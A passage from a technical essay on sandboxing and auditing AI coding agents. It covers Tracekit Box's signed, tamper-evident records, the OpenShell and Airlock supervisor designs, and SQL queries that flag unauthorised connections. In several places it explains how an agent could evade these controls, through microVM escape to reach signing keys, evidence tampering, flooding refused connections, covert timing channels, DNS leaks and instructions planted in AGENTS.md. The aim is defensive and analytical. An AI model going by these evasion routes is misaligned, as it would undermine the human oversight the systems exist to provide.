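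| 4 | The protected resource doesn't exist inside the sandbox | A microVM with no network card |

The project has scored 26 products and supplies a program for testing a sandbox directly. It also has fixed rules for deciding whether a sandbox addresses particular threats. To count as addressing data theft, for example, a sandbox must score at least 2 for files, network and credentials.

In an article, Coder's chief executive tried to score OpenAI's July environment from public statements, giving the network a 2 and credentials and control over actions 0 or 1 each. The statements lacked the detail needed to score isolation, resource limits or files. The article mistakenly places the proxy inside the sandbox. According to OpenAI, the proxy was a shared server elsewhere in the research network, which is why one flaw could help so many agents.

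The scale is useful because it separates a setting that a program can ignore from a barrier that it would have to break, but it doesn't measure whether the rule is good. In the attack on Claude Cowork, for example, the proxy enforced its allowlist correctly and the files still left through an approved host. Most of the published scores come from product documentation rather than tests.

The taxonomy's advice on combining products could also mislead buyers, because it takes the highest score at each layer without accounting for how one product can weaken another. For example, gVisor hides most of a program's system calls from an eBPF monitor on the host, so an operator who used both would get weaker records than the monitor's score suggests.

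Coder's chief executive also points out that the taxonomy has no layer for stopping an agent after it escapes, and that its score for records doesn't include how quickly a warning reaches a person. A fast warning wouldn't have been enough in June, because OpenAI's on-call staff investigated the alert, identified the test that caused it and let the test continue.

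## Tracekit Box: a microVM with signed records of every exit

Part of the evidence in METR's investigation of OpenAI's July incident came from machines that the agents had controlled, and METR couldn't rule out that the agents had edited that evidence. Tracekit Box, an open-source prototype from October 2026, keeps its records where the agent can't reach them and makes later changes to them detectable. The signer, a program on the host, allows or blocks network connections, commands and file changes, and signs a record of what crosses the boundary of the Firecracker microVM.

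Three vsock ports connect the guest to the host. The host uses the first to send commands and to collect results and changed files. The second carries web traffic, including calls to the model, to the proxy that checks destinations and adds real keys. The guest reads its settings at start-up through the third, which the host then closes.

Ghosh chose to record only at the microVM's exits, because hostile code could tamper with a monitor inside the guest, such as an eBPF probe. These records miss everything that stays inside, but Ghosh thinks this is the right tradeoff because an action has to leave the microVM to do harm elsewhere. That seems right for stolen keys and damaged repositories, though an investigator will have less evidence of how an attack began.

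### A job from start to exported record

For the test-fixing job, an operator could use these commands, adapted from Ghosh's examples:

```
tkbox run --name fix --image python:3.12-slim --workspace . \
    --allow pypi --secret API_KEY=env:API_KEY@api.service.example
tkbox exec fix -- pip install pytest requests
tkbox exec fix -- pytest
tkbox stop fix
tkbox diff fix
tkbox apply fix
tkbox export fix -o fix.tkb
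tracekit verify fix.tkb --trust fix.trust.json
```

The `run` command copies the project onto a read-only disk for the guest. It leaves out the `.git` folder, files that Git ignores, and files likely to contain credentials, such as `.env`. If one of the remaining files contains the API key, the job doesn't start. The agent's edits to the project go onto a second disk that starts empty, so when the job ends, that disk contains exactly what the job changed. Anything the agent writes outside the project folder disappears when the microVM stops.

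Before `exec` runs a command, it sends the signer the command line, working folder and environment variables. This description has to match what the guest will run. Changing `PATH`, for example, could make `pip` start a different program, so Tracekit Box doesn't let an individual command set it.

The record has no separate entries for programs that the command starts. If the harness runs on the host and sends each tool call through `exec`, the record contains every command the model proposed. But if the harness runs inside the microVM, as Claude Code can in Ghosh's GitHub workflow, a single entry may cover the whole session.

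A harness on the host needs its own user account, because any program that runs under the same account as the daemon (the background program that manages the microVMs) can approve its own connections to unlisted hosts.

The `stop` command closes the network and saves the agent's changes as a patch. The record stays open so that `apply` can add an entry for each file it writes to the repository. `export` then closes the record and saves it with a second file containing the information needed to check it. `verify` can check the record on a computer with no network connection.

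### Checking the patch file by file

A patch from a hostile guest could exploit a difference between what a checker reads and what Git writes. Fuzzing found one such difference. A patch that creates or deletes a file normally uses `/dev/null` to stand in for the missing version. Tracekit Box always read it that way, but Git treated it as a real file called `dev/null` if a certain other line was absent. Tracekit Box now refuses these patches.

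`tkbox apply` parses the patch under strict rules and checks that Git parses it the same way. It then builds the new files in a temporary folder rather than running `git apply` on the repository. The user's Git settings are turned off during this step so that the patch can't trigger their filters or hooks. Finally, it sends the signer each file's path, its permissions and a fingerprint of its new contents.

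If the signer refuses any file, `apply` writes nothing. Otherwise it checks that nobody has changed the project in the meantime, then writes each file itself. If a write fails partway through, it lists the files it has already written but doesn't restore the old versions.

Changes to some files also need the operator's explicit consent, through the option `--allow-sensitive`:

| Files | Examples | What a hostile change could do |
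|---|---|---|
| Automation | `.github/workflows`, `.gitlab-ci.yml`, `.husky` | Run the agent's code at the next commit or push |
| Git settings | `.gitignore`, `.gitattributes` | Change which files Git tracks or how it processes them |
| Settings for the next session | `tkbox.yaml`, `.envrc`, `.vscode/tasks.json` | Give the next agent more access, or run code on a developer's machine |
| Credentials | `.npmrc`, `.netrc`, private keys | Replace login details or redirect package downloads |

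These rules would stop the malicious Git hook in Hempel and colleagues' example. A patch can't change anything in `.git`, where hooks are normally stored, and the list includes `.husky`, where some projects keep theirs. But the list doesn't include AGENTS.md, the file Bao and colleagues used to carry an instruction from one agent session to the next.

The signer also receives only a fingerprint of each file, so it can reject a change to a particular path but can't detect a back door in ordinary source code. The next person to run the tests will run whatever the agent wrote. Someone still has to read the patch, but Ghosh's example GitHub workflow limits this risk by splitting the work into three jobs. The first runs the agent in the microVM, the second runs the changed code without access to secrets, and the third can write to the repository but runs no code from it.

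### Decisions and observations

The record contains two kinds of entry, decisions and observations. A decision means that the signer checked an action against its rules before the action happened. A later entry gives the outcome. An observation is a statement the signer signs without ruling on it.

| Event in the test-fixing job | Entry |
|---|---|
| The operator starts the job | Observations of the settings and the user's task |
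| The harness runs `pip install` | Decision on the command |
| Pip connects to pypi.org | Decision on the address |
| The proxy inserts the API key in a request | Observation of the key's name and the host |
| `curl` tries to reach collector.example | Decision on the address, then an observation that the proxy refused the connection |
| The operator applies the patch | Decision on each file |

Ghosh labels an observation "trusted" if it comes from Tracekit Box itself, as the settings do, and "untrusted" if it depends on data from the guest. The exported file contains only a fingerprint of each observation's content and the content's size. A reader can therefore confirm that an observation exists and hasn't changed, but needs another source for the content itself.

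The decisions alone can be misleading. In Ghosh's demonstration, the decision on example.com was to allow the connection, but the connection never opened. The signer attached a warning to that decision, but it attached warnings from the same two rules to all 39 connections. Most of these were probably ordinary package downloads, so the warnings wouldn't help a reviewer find the suspicious connection.

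### Detecting one altered record

A hash function such as SHA-256 turns any piece of data into a short fingerprint, or hash. Changing one character of the data produces a completely different hash. In a hash chain, each hash covers both the newest record and the hash before it. Crosby and Wallach, in *Efficient Data Structures for Tamper-Evident Logging*, write this as:

```
C(n) = H( C(n-1) || X(n) )
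```

Here `X(n)` is the newest record, `H` is the hash function and `||` joins two pieces of data. Suppose a short run has four records:

1. The signer allows `pip install`.
2. The signer allows a connection to pypi.org.
3. The proxy refuses a connection to collector.example.
4. The signer allows a change to `client.py`.

If someone edits record 3 to hide the attempted leak, `C(3)` and `C(4)` both change. Anyone who kept the original `C(4)` can detect the edit by recalculating the chain. However, checking one old record this way means processing every record after it, which is slow in a long log.

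A Merkle tree makes the check faster by hashing the records in pairs:

```
           R
         /   \
        P     Q
       / \   / \
     L1  L2 L3  L4
```

`L1` to `L4` are the hashes of the four records. `P` is the hash of `L1` and `L2` together, `Q` is the hash of `L3` and `L4`, and the root `R` is the hash of `P` and `Q`. Editing record 3 changes `L3`, `Q` and `R`. To check record 3 against the original root, a reader needs only the record, `L4` and `P`. The reader calculates `L3`, then `Q`, then `R`, and compares `R` with the original root. This is called an inclusion proof.

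Tracekit follows the tree design in *Certificate Transparency* (Laurie, Langley and Kasper, 2013), a standard for public logs of website certificates that the IETF's *Certificate Transparency Version 2.0* replaced in 2021. The 2013 design adds one byte in front of a record before hashing it and a different byte in front of a pair of hashes, so that nobody can pass off a pair of hashes as a record. The tree in Ghosh's demonstration had 5,978 entries, apparently from many runs, and an inclusion proof for any of them would need at most 13 hashes.

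The signer creates a checkpoint by signing the root together with the number of records. The `verify` command checks the signatures on the checkpoint and on every record in the run. It then recalculates the run's hash chain and checks inclusion proofs for the first and last records. The records between them don't need their own proofs because the chain connects them.

### Witnesses, and records that were false from the start

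An attacker who has the signer's key can defeat all of these checks by editing record 3, recalculating every hash and signing everything again. The new log would be consistent. Transparency.dev's *Verifiable data structures* explains that only someone with an earlier copy of the root could detect the change.

A witness is a program that keeps such a copy, ideally on a machine that somebody else controls. As the software project *Witness* (2025) describes it, the witness stores the latest checkpoint from each log. When a log grows, the witness accepts a new checkpoint only with proof that the old records are still there, unchanged and in the same order. It then adds its own signature to the checkpoint.

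Suppose the witness has stored `R` and the signer adds a fifth record, whose hash is `L5`. The new root is the hash of `R` and `L5` together, so the witness needs only `L5` to check it. If an attacker has edited record 3, the first four records produce a different root and they can't construct a valid proof from `R`, so the witness refuses to sign.

This also protects against an operator who shows different versions of a log to different people, as long as readers require the witness's signature. But a witness may accept the first checkpoint from a log on trust, so it can't detect edits made before that checkpoint.

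A witness also doesn't check whether the records are true. According to *tlog cosignature*, its signature means only that, at a stated time, the largest consistent version of the log it had observed had a certain root. Crosby and Wallach likewise acknowledge that their method can't keep "junk" out of a log. If the signer signs a false record, it will pass every later check. These tools establish integrity, meaning that nobody has changed a record since it was signed, but whether the record was true to begin with depends on who could use the signing key.

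In all of Ghosh's tests, the signer ran on the same host and under the same user account as the daemon, without a witness. Any program under that account could have signed false records. Firecracker ran under that account too, without its jailer, so an agent that broke out of the microVM might have been able to reach the signing key, although Firecracker's seccomp filter would still have restricted what the agent could do.

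The `verify` report shows this weakness in the line "Assurance: dev". It also marks the check for witness signatures as passed because the configuration required none, so the assurance line is a better guide than the number of passes. An operator can improve this setup by giving the signer its own account and adding a witness on another machine, but the signer can't yet run on a different host.

### Stopping the job when a record fails

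A system fails closed if it refuses an action when the component that should decide on it or record it is unavailable. gVisor's trace points and Tetragon's recording don't fail closed, so the program continues if a record is lost. Tracekit Box is stricter, which is more practical for it because few events cross its boundary. Ghosh's demonstration produced 102 records, while recording every read and write in a typical coding job could produce hundreds of thousands.

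| Failure | Response |
|---|---|
| No signer is running when the daemon starts | The daemon refuses to start, unless the operator chooses to run without records |
| The signer stops responding | Tracekit Box refuses every new command, connection and file write |
| The signer can't take an important observation, such as the use of a key | The microVM stops, and Tracekit Box adds a gap entry to the record |
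| The signer can't take the result of an action it allowed | The job continues, and a gap entry counts the missing result |
| The daemon crashes | Nobody can apply that job's patch or export its record |

A gap entry gives the type of record lost, the number lost and the reason. Without it, a reader couldn't tell whether nothing had happened or a record was missing. Tracekit Box makes one deliberate exception, for connections that it refuses itself. It records up to 20 of these a second and only counts the rest. An agent could therefore hide the destinations of some failed attempts by making thousands of others, but all the attempts would still be counted.

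Because of this strictness, a daemon crash can waste an hour of an agent's work, and hostile code might be able to stop its own job by causing more observations than the signer can process. Stopping the job is a small loss if the agent is fixing a test, but it could cause an outage if the agent is running a live service.

The signer can also order the daemon to pause or kill a microVM. The daemon checks for orders every two seconds during the first minute and about every 15 seconds after that. An agent could send out a lot of data in 15 seconds, so pausing or killing the microVM mainly limits further damage.

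### What the tests cover

Ghosh built and tested this first version, and nobody else seems to have published a test of it. All 13 end-to-end checks passed on a host with KVM in 28.5 seconds, which included downloading the system image and starting the microVM. One check confirmed that the guest had no network card. Another applied a patch, then exported and verified a record of 64 entries. A separate test confirmed that the daemon won't start without a signer.

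Each check covers one typical case, so the checks show that the parts work, but not that they would withstand a persistent attacker. The 28.5 seconds includes deliberate waits and a package installation. Ghosh hasn't measured how long a microVM takes to start or how much delay each decision adds.

The 15 fuzz targets are more demanding because each checks that a stated rule holds for any input. One rule is that Tracekit Box must find every file that Git would find in a patch it accepts. Three of the nine bugs that fuzzing found were outside the proxy, and one of these affected the record. Some shells treat a name that begins with `%` as a reference to a running job, so the signed command might not have named the program that ran. Tracekit Box now refuses such names. One of the nine bugs turned up only after the main round of fuzzing, so others may remain.

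The hand-typed demonstration produced 102 records. Of these, 46 are decisions, on seven commands and 39 connections, and 46 are their results. The other ten cover the settings, two refused connections, one use of a key, one approval request, and the start and end of the run. None of the 102 is a decision on a file. The demonstration therefore shows what a valid record looks like, but not whether an investigator could use such records to follow a long agent session.

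Ghosh plans to add a process monitor inside the guest and compare its records with those from the exits. If a connection reached the proxy but the monitor had no record of a program that could have made it, that would suggest someone had tampered with the monitor.

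## OpenShell and Airlock: moving the supervisor away from the agent

A supervisor is the trusted component that applies policy to an agent, holds its credentials and records its actions. Tracekit Box performs these tasks on the same host as the microVM, so an agent that escaped the microVM might reach the keys and records. OpenShell, an open-source runtime from the chip maker NVIDIA, first ran the supervisor inside the agent's sandbox but later moved it out. Airlock, a November 2026 research prototype from Imperial College London and Microsoft, builds on OpenShell and also prevents the host from reading or changing the supervisor's memory.

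### How OpenShell runs an agent

Abdollahi and colleagues describe the version of OpenShell from which they built Airlock. Users deal only with the gateway, which accepts a policy and credentials for each agent and passes on the user's requests. A compute driver then starts a sandbox for the agent and a separate environment for its supervisor, for example in two containers. The driver also blocks every network route out of the sandbox except the channel to the supervisor.

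Inside the sandbox, a small program called the broker starts the agent. When pip calls `connect` in the test-fixing job, a seccomp filter passes the call to the broker, which forwards it to the supervisor. The supervisor checks the policy, opens the real connection and relays the data. It also replaces fake credentials with real ones, as Tracekit Box's proxy does. NVIDIA says that for some kinds of web traffic, the supervisor can let an agent read from a service but not write to it.

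Landlock, a Linux security module, controls which files the agent can access. The operator lists the folders the agent may read and those it may also change, and the kernel refuses all other file access. The same limits apply to programs the agent starts. Permission for a folder covers everything in it, so a rule that gives access to `/work` also gives access to the key file `/work/.env`.

According to NVIDIA's *How OpenShell Works*, file rules take effect when the sandbox starts, and the operator has to recreate the sandbox to change them. Network rules can change while the agent runs. An operator could therefore withdraw access to a compromised package server during a job, but couldn't block access to a folder without interrupting the job.

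OpenShell also has a policy prover. According to NVIDIA (2026), it checks whether a policy allows more than the organisation's upper limit. If so, it can give an example of an action that exceeds the limit, much as Cedar's solver finds a request on which two policies disagree.

Biometric Update's *Nvidia adds identity and delegated authority controls for AI agents* reports a test in which agents spent nine hours over twelve sessions trying to get write access to a protected GitHub repository. An AI reviewer made 416 decisions and wrongly approved one proposal that included write access. OpenShell rejected the resulting policy before it took effect. This supports putting a fixed check behind a model's judgement, but NVIDIA ran the test itself. The reported result also concerns approvals, so it is weak evidence about whether an agent could break out of the sandbox.

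### What a compromised sandbox exposes

*How OpenShell Works* describes the earlier design, in which a supervisor ran inside each sandbox and started the agent as a restricted child process. The network proxy and an OPA policy engine ran there too, and the supervisor received credentials from the gateway. An agent that gained full control of its sandbox could have read the credentials, ignored the policy and changed any log entries that the supervisor hadn't yet sent to the gateway.

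In the current design, the broker, the seccomp filter and the Landlock rules are still in the agent's environment. An agent that takes over the broker can send the supervisor any request, but the supervisor still checks each one. The separation is weaker if the sandbox and the supervisor are containers on the same machine, because they share the host's kernel. An agent that exploited a kernel flaw such as Copy Fail could remove its own file rules and then take over the supervisor in the other container.

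| Design | What shares the agent's environment | What an attacker would generally need to reach the supervisor |
|---|---|---|
| Earlier OpenShell | The supervisor, proxy, policy engine, credentials and file rules | Full control of the sandbox |
| Current OpenShell, in two containers | The broker and file rules | A bug in the host's kernel |
| Airlock | The broker, an inner set of file rules and a program that launches the sandbox | A bug in the supervisor's own virtual machine, or in the hardware or firmware that protects it |

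Even if the agent ran in an ordinary virtual machine, an escape would expose the supervisor, because the host can read the supervisor's memory, including any keys in it.

### Confidential virtual machines and attestation

In a confidential virtual machine, the processor and a small amount of trusted firmware stop the host operating system from reading or changing the guest's private memory and processor state. The host still supplies memory and schedules the guest. AMD and Intel sell processors that can do this, but Airlock uses Arm's Confidential Compute Architecture (CCA). In CCA, firmware called the Realm Management Monitor, rather than the host, controls the guest's page tables.

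Before sending keys to such a machine, a user needs evidence of what software is running on it, which attestation provides. The firmware calculates a hash of the machine's initial state, including its kernel and start-up options, and puts it in a token. The token also contains a fresh challenge value, so nobody can pass off an old token as new. A verifier compares the hash with the expected one. A match shows which software the machine started with, but not that the software is free of bugs or that an attacker hasn't taken it over since.

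Airlock runs the agent and the supervisor in separate confidential virtual machines (VMs), because a shared one would protect both from the host but leave the supervisor exposed to the agent. The agent VM contains OpenShell's sandbox, with the agent, its tools and the broker. The supervisor VM contains the supervisor, the gateway and the compute driver.

Each VM has a policy that identifies the other by its hash. The firmware checks that the policies agree, then gives the two VMs an area of memory that the host can't access. It also stops the agent VM from sharing memory with the host. Nobody can change these policies once they take effect, and the supervisor VM's token includes them, so a verifier can confirm that the agent's only partner is the expected supervisor.

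### One file write and one HTTPS connection

The agent VM has a file-system device and a socket device, and programs in the supervisor VM handle the requests from both. It has no disk or network card that it can use independently. The two VMs exchange data through shared memory and signal each other through the firmware, without going through the host.

Suppose the agent edits `client.py` to fix the failing test. When its editor opens the file, Landlock makes the first check. The agent VM's kernel then sends a request through the file-system device to a policy engine in the supervisor VM. The engine checks the path against the same user policy and records which rights it granted. When the editor writes the new text, the agent VM's kernel keeps it in memory and later sends it in a batch to the supervisor VM, which saves it in a folder on its own disk.

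An attacker who takes over the agent VM's kernel can switch off Landlock but not the second check. The second check still seems to have a weak point, because the user's file rules apply to requests from the sandbox's user account, and the agent VM's kernel supplies the account number on each request. A hostile kernel could label a request as coming from the administrator account, and then only Airlock's start-up rules for that account would apply. Those rules need to be strict enough on their own.

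A new HTTPS connection, such as pip's connection to pypi.org, takes a longer route:

1. The broker catches the `connect` call and sends it to the supervisor through the socket device.
2. The supervisor checks the request against the network policy.
3. The agent ledger, a record-keeping program in the supervisor VM, sends a record of the connection to Azure Confidential Ledger, which accepts new entries but never changes or removes old ones.
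4. When the outside ledger returns a signed receipt, a gate in the supervisor VM opens the connection, and the supervisor relays the data.

### Why the connection waits and the file doesn't

Airlock delays the connection because nobody can take back data that has left the machine. If the agent later took over the supervisor VM and deleted its local records, the outside ledger would still show that the connection had been opened. The delay averages 259 milliseconds, most of it spent waiting for the ledger to respond.

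A file change stays on a disk that the supervisor VM controls, so there is less need to wait for the ledger. File requests are also far more common. In the busiest test run, the agent's programs made about 236,000 of them. Waiting for the ledger's median response time of 213 milliseconds on each request in turn would have added about 14 hours to the run. Airlock instead carries out each request immediately and sends the records to the ledger in batches, by default every two seconds. Preparing the file records in that run took 0.16 seconds. The ledger lists each file the agent creates, renames or deletes, but combines all reads and writes of one open file into a single record.

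DNS queries and unencrypted web requests don't wait either, although they can carry data out. This exception is hard to justify except by speed. If the supervisor allowed a DNS query like those in the `ping` attack on Claude Code, the query would leave before its record was safe. An HTTPS connection waits only when it opens, and the ledger doesn't store what passes through it.

The records form a hash chain, as in Tracekit Box. Each entry in the outside ledger contains a fingerprint of a batch of records and as many of those records as fit in 8 kilobytes. When the agent is idle, Airlock still adds a record every ten seconds, so a reader can tell an idle agent from a ledger that has stopped working.

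The chain begins with the supervisor VM's attestation token, which identifies the key used to write to the ledger. This lets an outsider check which software produced the records and which policy was in force, whereas Tracekit Box's signatures show only that someone with the signing key produced a record. Abdollahi and colleagues suggest that a booking website could use Airlock's evidence to check that a request came from an agent under a known policy.

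### What survives each kind of compromise

| What the attacker controls | What still works | What the operator loses |
|---|---|---|
| The agent VM, including its kernel | The supervisor's network policy, outer file checks, credentials and records | The broker, the seccomp filter and Landlock |
| The host | The supervisor's policy checks and records, and the secrecy of data passing between the VMs | Guaranteed service, because the host can delay or stop either VM |
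| A network route that avoids the supervisor | The secrecy of the credentials | Control and records of what leaves by that route |
| The supervisor VM | Entries already in the outside ledger | Policy enforcement, the credentials and the reliability of later records |

If the supervisor VM is compromised, the attacker can also destroy records from the last few seconds that haven't reached the outside ledger. These could include file accesses, DNS queries and unencrypted web requests, but not the opening of an HTTPS connection. Deleting older local records wouldn't affect the copies in the ledger. If a batch was too large for one entry, the ledger would still show how many records were missing.

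All this assumes that the processor and firmware work correctly, the user has chosen sensible policies and the outside ledger is append-only. Microsoft runs that ledger and employs four of the eight researchers. An organisation that doesn't want to depend on Microsoft would need a different ledger.

Airlock doesn't prevent the misuse of services that the policy permits, so an upload like the one in the Claude Cowork attack could still succeed. It also doesn't guarantee protection against denial of service. Because every new HTTPS connection waits for a receipt, an outage at the ledger would stop the agent from opening new connections to its model.

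Some covert channels also remain. The agent VM still calls on the host when it uses certain device settings, and a compromised host could read a message hidden in the values or the timing. The two could also communicate by competing for shared parts of the processor. In the test-fixing job, an agent working with a compromised host might slowly leak the project's source code through these channels, but not the API key, because the agent VM never receives it.

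The host could also replace stored data with an older version. Airlock needs a separate layer of disk protection to detect this. Adding such a layer to the prototype slowed large reads from 112 to 14 megabytes a second, mainly because the test board has no encryption hardware.

### Measurements from a board without the Arm hardware

Abdollahi and colleagues report that no commercial processor with CCA was available when they wrote. They checked that Airlock worked in QEMU, which can imitate CCA but not its speed. They ran the timings on a Radxa Rock 5B+, a low-cost computer board that lacks the hardware to protect confidential memory, so software imitates the separation of that memory.

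In the signalling test, two VMs exchanged a signal and a reply 50,000 times. The median round trip took 9.9 microseconds through Airlock's firmware and 38.5 when the host relayed the signals. The socket test compared Airlock with two processes in the same VM. Airlock was slightly faster for a 64-byte message, at 30.9 microseconds instead of 35.3, but took more than twice as long for a 256-kilobyte one.

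Socket throughput was 51–70% lower than within one VM. Even the slowest result, 4.1 gigabits a second, was above the 2.5 that the board's network card can carry, so the socket device is unlikely to limit an agent's downloads on this board.

The file-system tests compared Airlock with an agent VM that used the disk directly:

| Access pattern | Effect of Airlock |
|---|---|
| Reads from memory | Within 1% |
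| Writes to memory, saved to disk later | No measurable difference |
| Reads straight from disk | Throughput 3–6% lower |
| Large writes straight to disk | Throughput 10% lower |
| Small writes straight to disk | Throughput 13% lower, delay 14% longer |
| Small writes that must each be safely on disk before the next | Throughput 35% lower, delay 2.5 times as long |

The researchers' headline figure, a loss of less than 15%, excludes the last row. Most coding work depends more on the first two rows, but an agent that tests a database could make many writes of the kind in the last row.

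The team also ran 12 agent tasks six times each, using the agent OpenClaw and a model from OpenAI. The average task took 85.7 seconds with OpenShell in a single VM, 91.4 with Airlock and 95.0 with Airlock and its ledger. Airlock with its ledger added about 11%. The work done on the board itself took 33% longer even without the ledger, but most of each task was spent waiting for the model. Differences in the model's behaviour also affected the results. On disk-heavy tasks, for example, Airlock was 4% faster overall because the agent happened to take fewer steps.

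The baseline already ran in a simulated confidential VM, so these figures include only the overhead of splitting OpenShell across two VMs, not the overhead of moving from an ordinary container to a confidential VM. Abdollahi and colleagues expect the split to add less overhead on real CCA hardware, which may be able to deliver signals from the network card and disk more directly. But real hardware also makes memory checks that the board skips, so nobody yet knows the full overhead.

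### Fewer things to trust, but special hardware

Airlock removes the host's operating system from the trusted computing base for policy, credentials and records. This is its main advantage over Firecracker, where a serious bug in KVM could expose everything on the host. But the operator still has to trust the supervisor VM's own Linux kernel, the supervisor, the policy engines and the firmware. The total amount of trusted code is still large, though the agent can attack less of it directly.

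That part includes some kernel code. By default, the supervisor VM's kernel handles socket data from the agent VM, because this was faster on the board than using an ordinary program. A bug in that code could give a hostile agent control of the supervisor VM. Airlock can use an ordinary program instead, which would probably be safer against agents that are good at finding kernel flaws. The researchers analysed possible attacks but didn't report a test in which anyone tried to break in.

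Airlock is also a long way from deployment. The researchers expect it to suit NVIDIA's Vera and Microsoft's Cobalt processors, but it needs modified firmware as well as CCA. Hiding its signals completely from the host also requires a newer interrupt controller than the board has. Versions for AMD and Intel processors would require those companies' cooperation.

NVIDIA's Sentry puts the controls on separate hardware instead. It runs on a data processing unit, which has its own processor and handles a server's network traffic. Help Net Security's *NVIDIA wants AI agent safety enforced in silicon* (2026) reports that NVIDIA's design places the unit between the agent and its model, where Sentry can monitor the agent and stop it if it tries to cross its software boundary. NVIDIA promises containment within milliseconds, but HotHardware's *NVIDIA Rallies Over 100 Partners For Open Agent Safety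 Platform Launch* found few details about what that means. Sentry also requires particular hardware. Abdollahi and colleagues suggest that a similar unit could eventually do the supervisor VM's work.

OpenShell is much easier to adopt because it is free and runs on ordinary processors. It is now a project of the Cloud Native Computing Foundation, which also hosts Kubernetes (CNCF, *OpenShell*, 2026). More than 100 organisations are working with the wider NVIDIA platform, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *NVIDIA Launches Open Platform to Secure Autonomous AI Agents*, but that figure doesn't measure how many use OpenShell in production.

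An operator can get some of Airlock's benefits without CCA by running the agent in an ordinary virtual machine, keeping the supervisor outside it and sending records to a ledger on another system. If the ledger must confirm each record before a connection opens, the evidence of that connection will survive even if the agent escapes to the host. The keys and the policy won't be safe in that case. Airlock's extra protection would therefore matter most to operators who expect their agents could escape, or who rent machines from a company they don't fully trust.

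## Using the records to govern agents

Airlock's outside ledger can preserve a record after an agent has escaped, but somebody still has to find that record, connect it to a particular agent and act on it. An agent governance system consists of the people, rules and software that do this work, and it has five tasks.

| Task | Records that serve it | Question they answer |
|---|---|---|
| Register agents and their owners | A register with each agent's version, purpose and responsible person | Whose agent is this? |
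| Grant permissions | The change history of the rules, and the decision log | Who allowed this action, and under which rules? |
| Supervise runs | The harness's list of tool calls, the proxy log and process telemetry | What is the agent doing now? |
| Handle incidents | All of these joined together, with a list of the keys each run used | How far did the agent get, and which keys need replacing? |
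| Give evidence to auditors | A signed export or outside ledger, and notes of each review | Has anyone changed the records, and did anyone act on them? |

The register is the simplest of these records, but the others are hard to use without it. The supervisor, not the agent, should write the entries, and owners also need a verified identity. Maiti cites a 2026 red-team study in which an agent obeyed a stranger who had changed their display name to match the owner's.

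### One package download in three records

Suppose the test-fixing job runs in an ordinary container, with Tetragon on the host and a proxy that asks OPA about each connection. When the supervisor starts the container, it adds the run to the register. All the values here are invented:

```json
{"run": "run-318", "agent": "test-fixer", "owner": "d.ruiz",
 "node": "host-7", "container": "c41f",
 "started": "2026-10-07T09:11:58Z"}
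```

The agent then runs `pip install requests`. A kernel probe reports the connection, in simplified form:

```json
{"time": "2026-10-07T09:12:41.207Z",
 "node": "host-7", "container": "c41f",
 "pid": 5301, "process_started": "2026-10-07T09:12:40.655Z",
 "binary": "/usr/local/bin/pip", "arguments": "install requests",
 "source": "172.18.0.4:41822", "destination": "172.18.0.1:3128"}
```

The proxy writes its own record:

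```json
{"received": "2026-10-07T09:12:41.209Z", "container": "c41f",
 "client": "172.18.0.4:41822", "host": "pypi.org", "port": 443,
 "decision_id": "b20e91d7", "outcome": "opened"}
```

OPA's decision log contains this entry, again shortened:

```json
{"timestamp": "2026-10-07T09:12:41.211Z", "decision_id": "b20e91d7",
 "bundles": {"agents": {"revision": "7864d60d"}},
 "input": {"agent": "test-fixer", "run": "run-318",
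           "action": "connect", "host": "pypi.org", "port": 443},
 "result": {"decision": "allow", "reason": "package download"}}
```

The kernel event doesn't include pypi.org because pip connected to the proxy at 172.18.0.1. The proxy record includes the site but not the program. Both records contain `172.18.0.4:41822`, the container's address and the temporary port Linux assigned to the connection. Linux can reuse the port later, so the times must also match. The decision ID then links the proxy record to OPA's entry, and the container ID links the kernel event to the run and its owner.

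Together, the records show that process 5301 in d.ruiz's run-318 used pip to connect to pypi.org, and that revision 7864d60d of the rules allowed the connection as a package download.

The harness can also make processes traceable to the model's tool calls by recording the process ID and start time of the shell it opens for each call. An investigator can then follow pip's parent processes back to that shell. This is more reliable than the timing and text matching that Zheng and colleagues use, but it still fails if the agent hands the work to a scheduler such as cron.

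In a microVM, the process record would have to come from the less reliable monitor inside the guest.

### From a missing decision to a paused run

Once the records share these fields, a program can search for connections that nobody authorised. This query assumes that each kind of record has its own database table:

```sql
SELECT k.time, r.run, r.agent, k.binary, k.destination
FROM connections k
JOIN runs r
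  ON r.node = k.node AND r.container = k.container
 AND k.time BETWEEN r.started AND COALESCE(r.ended, NOW())
LEFT JOIN proxy_log p
  ON p.container = k.container AND p.client = k.source
 AND p.received BETWEEN k.time - INTERVAL '2 seconds'
                    AND k.time + INTERVAL '2 seconds'
LEFT JOIN decisions d
  ON d.decision_id = p.decision_id AND d.run = r.run
 AND d.host = p.host AND d.port = p.port
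WHERE (d.decision_id IS NULL
       OR (d.decision = 'deny' AND p.outcome = 'opened'))
  AND k.destination NOT LIKE '127.%'
  AND k.time < NOW() - INTERVAL '30 seconds';
```

The check looks for a proxy record and a decision for every connection, and returns the connections that have no decision or that opened despite a refusal. It ignores addresses that begin with 127, because test suites often start a small server and connect to it within the same container. It waits 30 seconds so that it doesn't treat a late record as missing.

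Suppose the agent writes a Python script that ignores the proxy settings and connects directly to collector.example. The kernel event contains that server's address, but the proxy has no record of the connection, so the query returns the event. A working firewall will already have blocked the connection, and the alert reports a failed attempt. If the firewall has a gap, this alert may be the first sign of it.

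The supervisor can respond by pausing the run. Docker can suspend every process in a container, and Firecracker can stop a microVM's virtual processors. Pausing preserves the contents of memory for investigators, while killing the run would destroy them. Pausing can't recover data that left during the 30 seconds, so the proxy still has to refuse any connection it can't get a decision on. A connection to anywhere other than the proxy looks suspicious with or without a matching record, so a separate rule could pause the run at once.

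If OPA's log drops an entry, the query raises a false alarm, but if the kernel probe drops an event, the query has nothing to check. An operator should therefore also run the comparison in reverse and look for approved connections without a kernel event. A few of these probably mean a full buffer, which calls for an alert but not a pause. If kernel events keep going missing while the proxy is still busy, someone may have turned the probe off.

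A run should stay paused until a named person records a reason for resuming it. For an agent that runs a live service, the operator might instead block new connections and leave the service running.

### What breaks the join

**Reused process numbers.** Linux numbers processes in sequence and returns to the low numbers when it reaches a limit, traditionally 32,768. A server that ran 1,000 jobs a day with 200 processes each would pass that limit about six times a day. Process 5301 could be pip in the morning and an unrelated shell in the afternoon, so the record also needs the machine and the process's start time. A process in a container has one number inside the container and another on the host, so a harness inside the container may report a different number from the probe.

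**Clock differences.** The kernel probe and the proxy share a clock if they run on the same host. OPA may run elsewhere, but its records can be matched by decision ID instead of by time. MicroVMs are harder because a guest restored from a snapshot can resume with its clock set to the time of the snapshot, so its events may look hours old until its clock is corrected. The host should add its own arrival time to every record from a guest.

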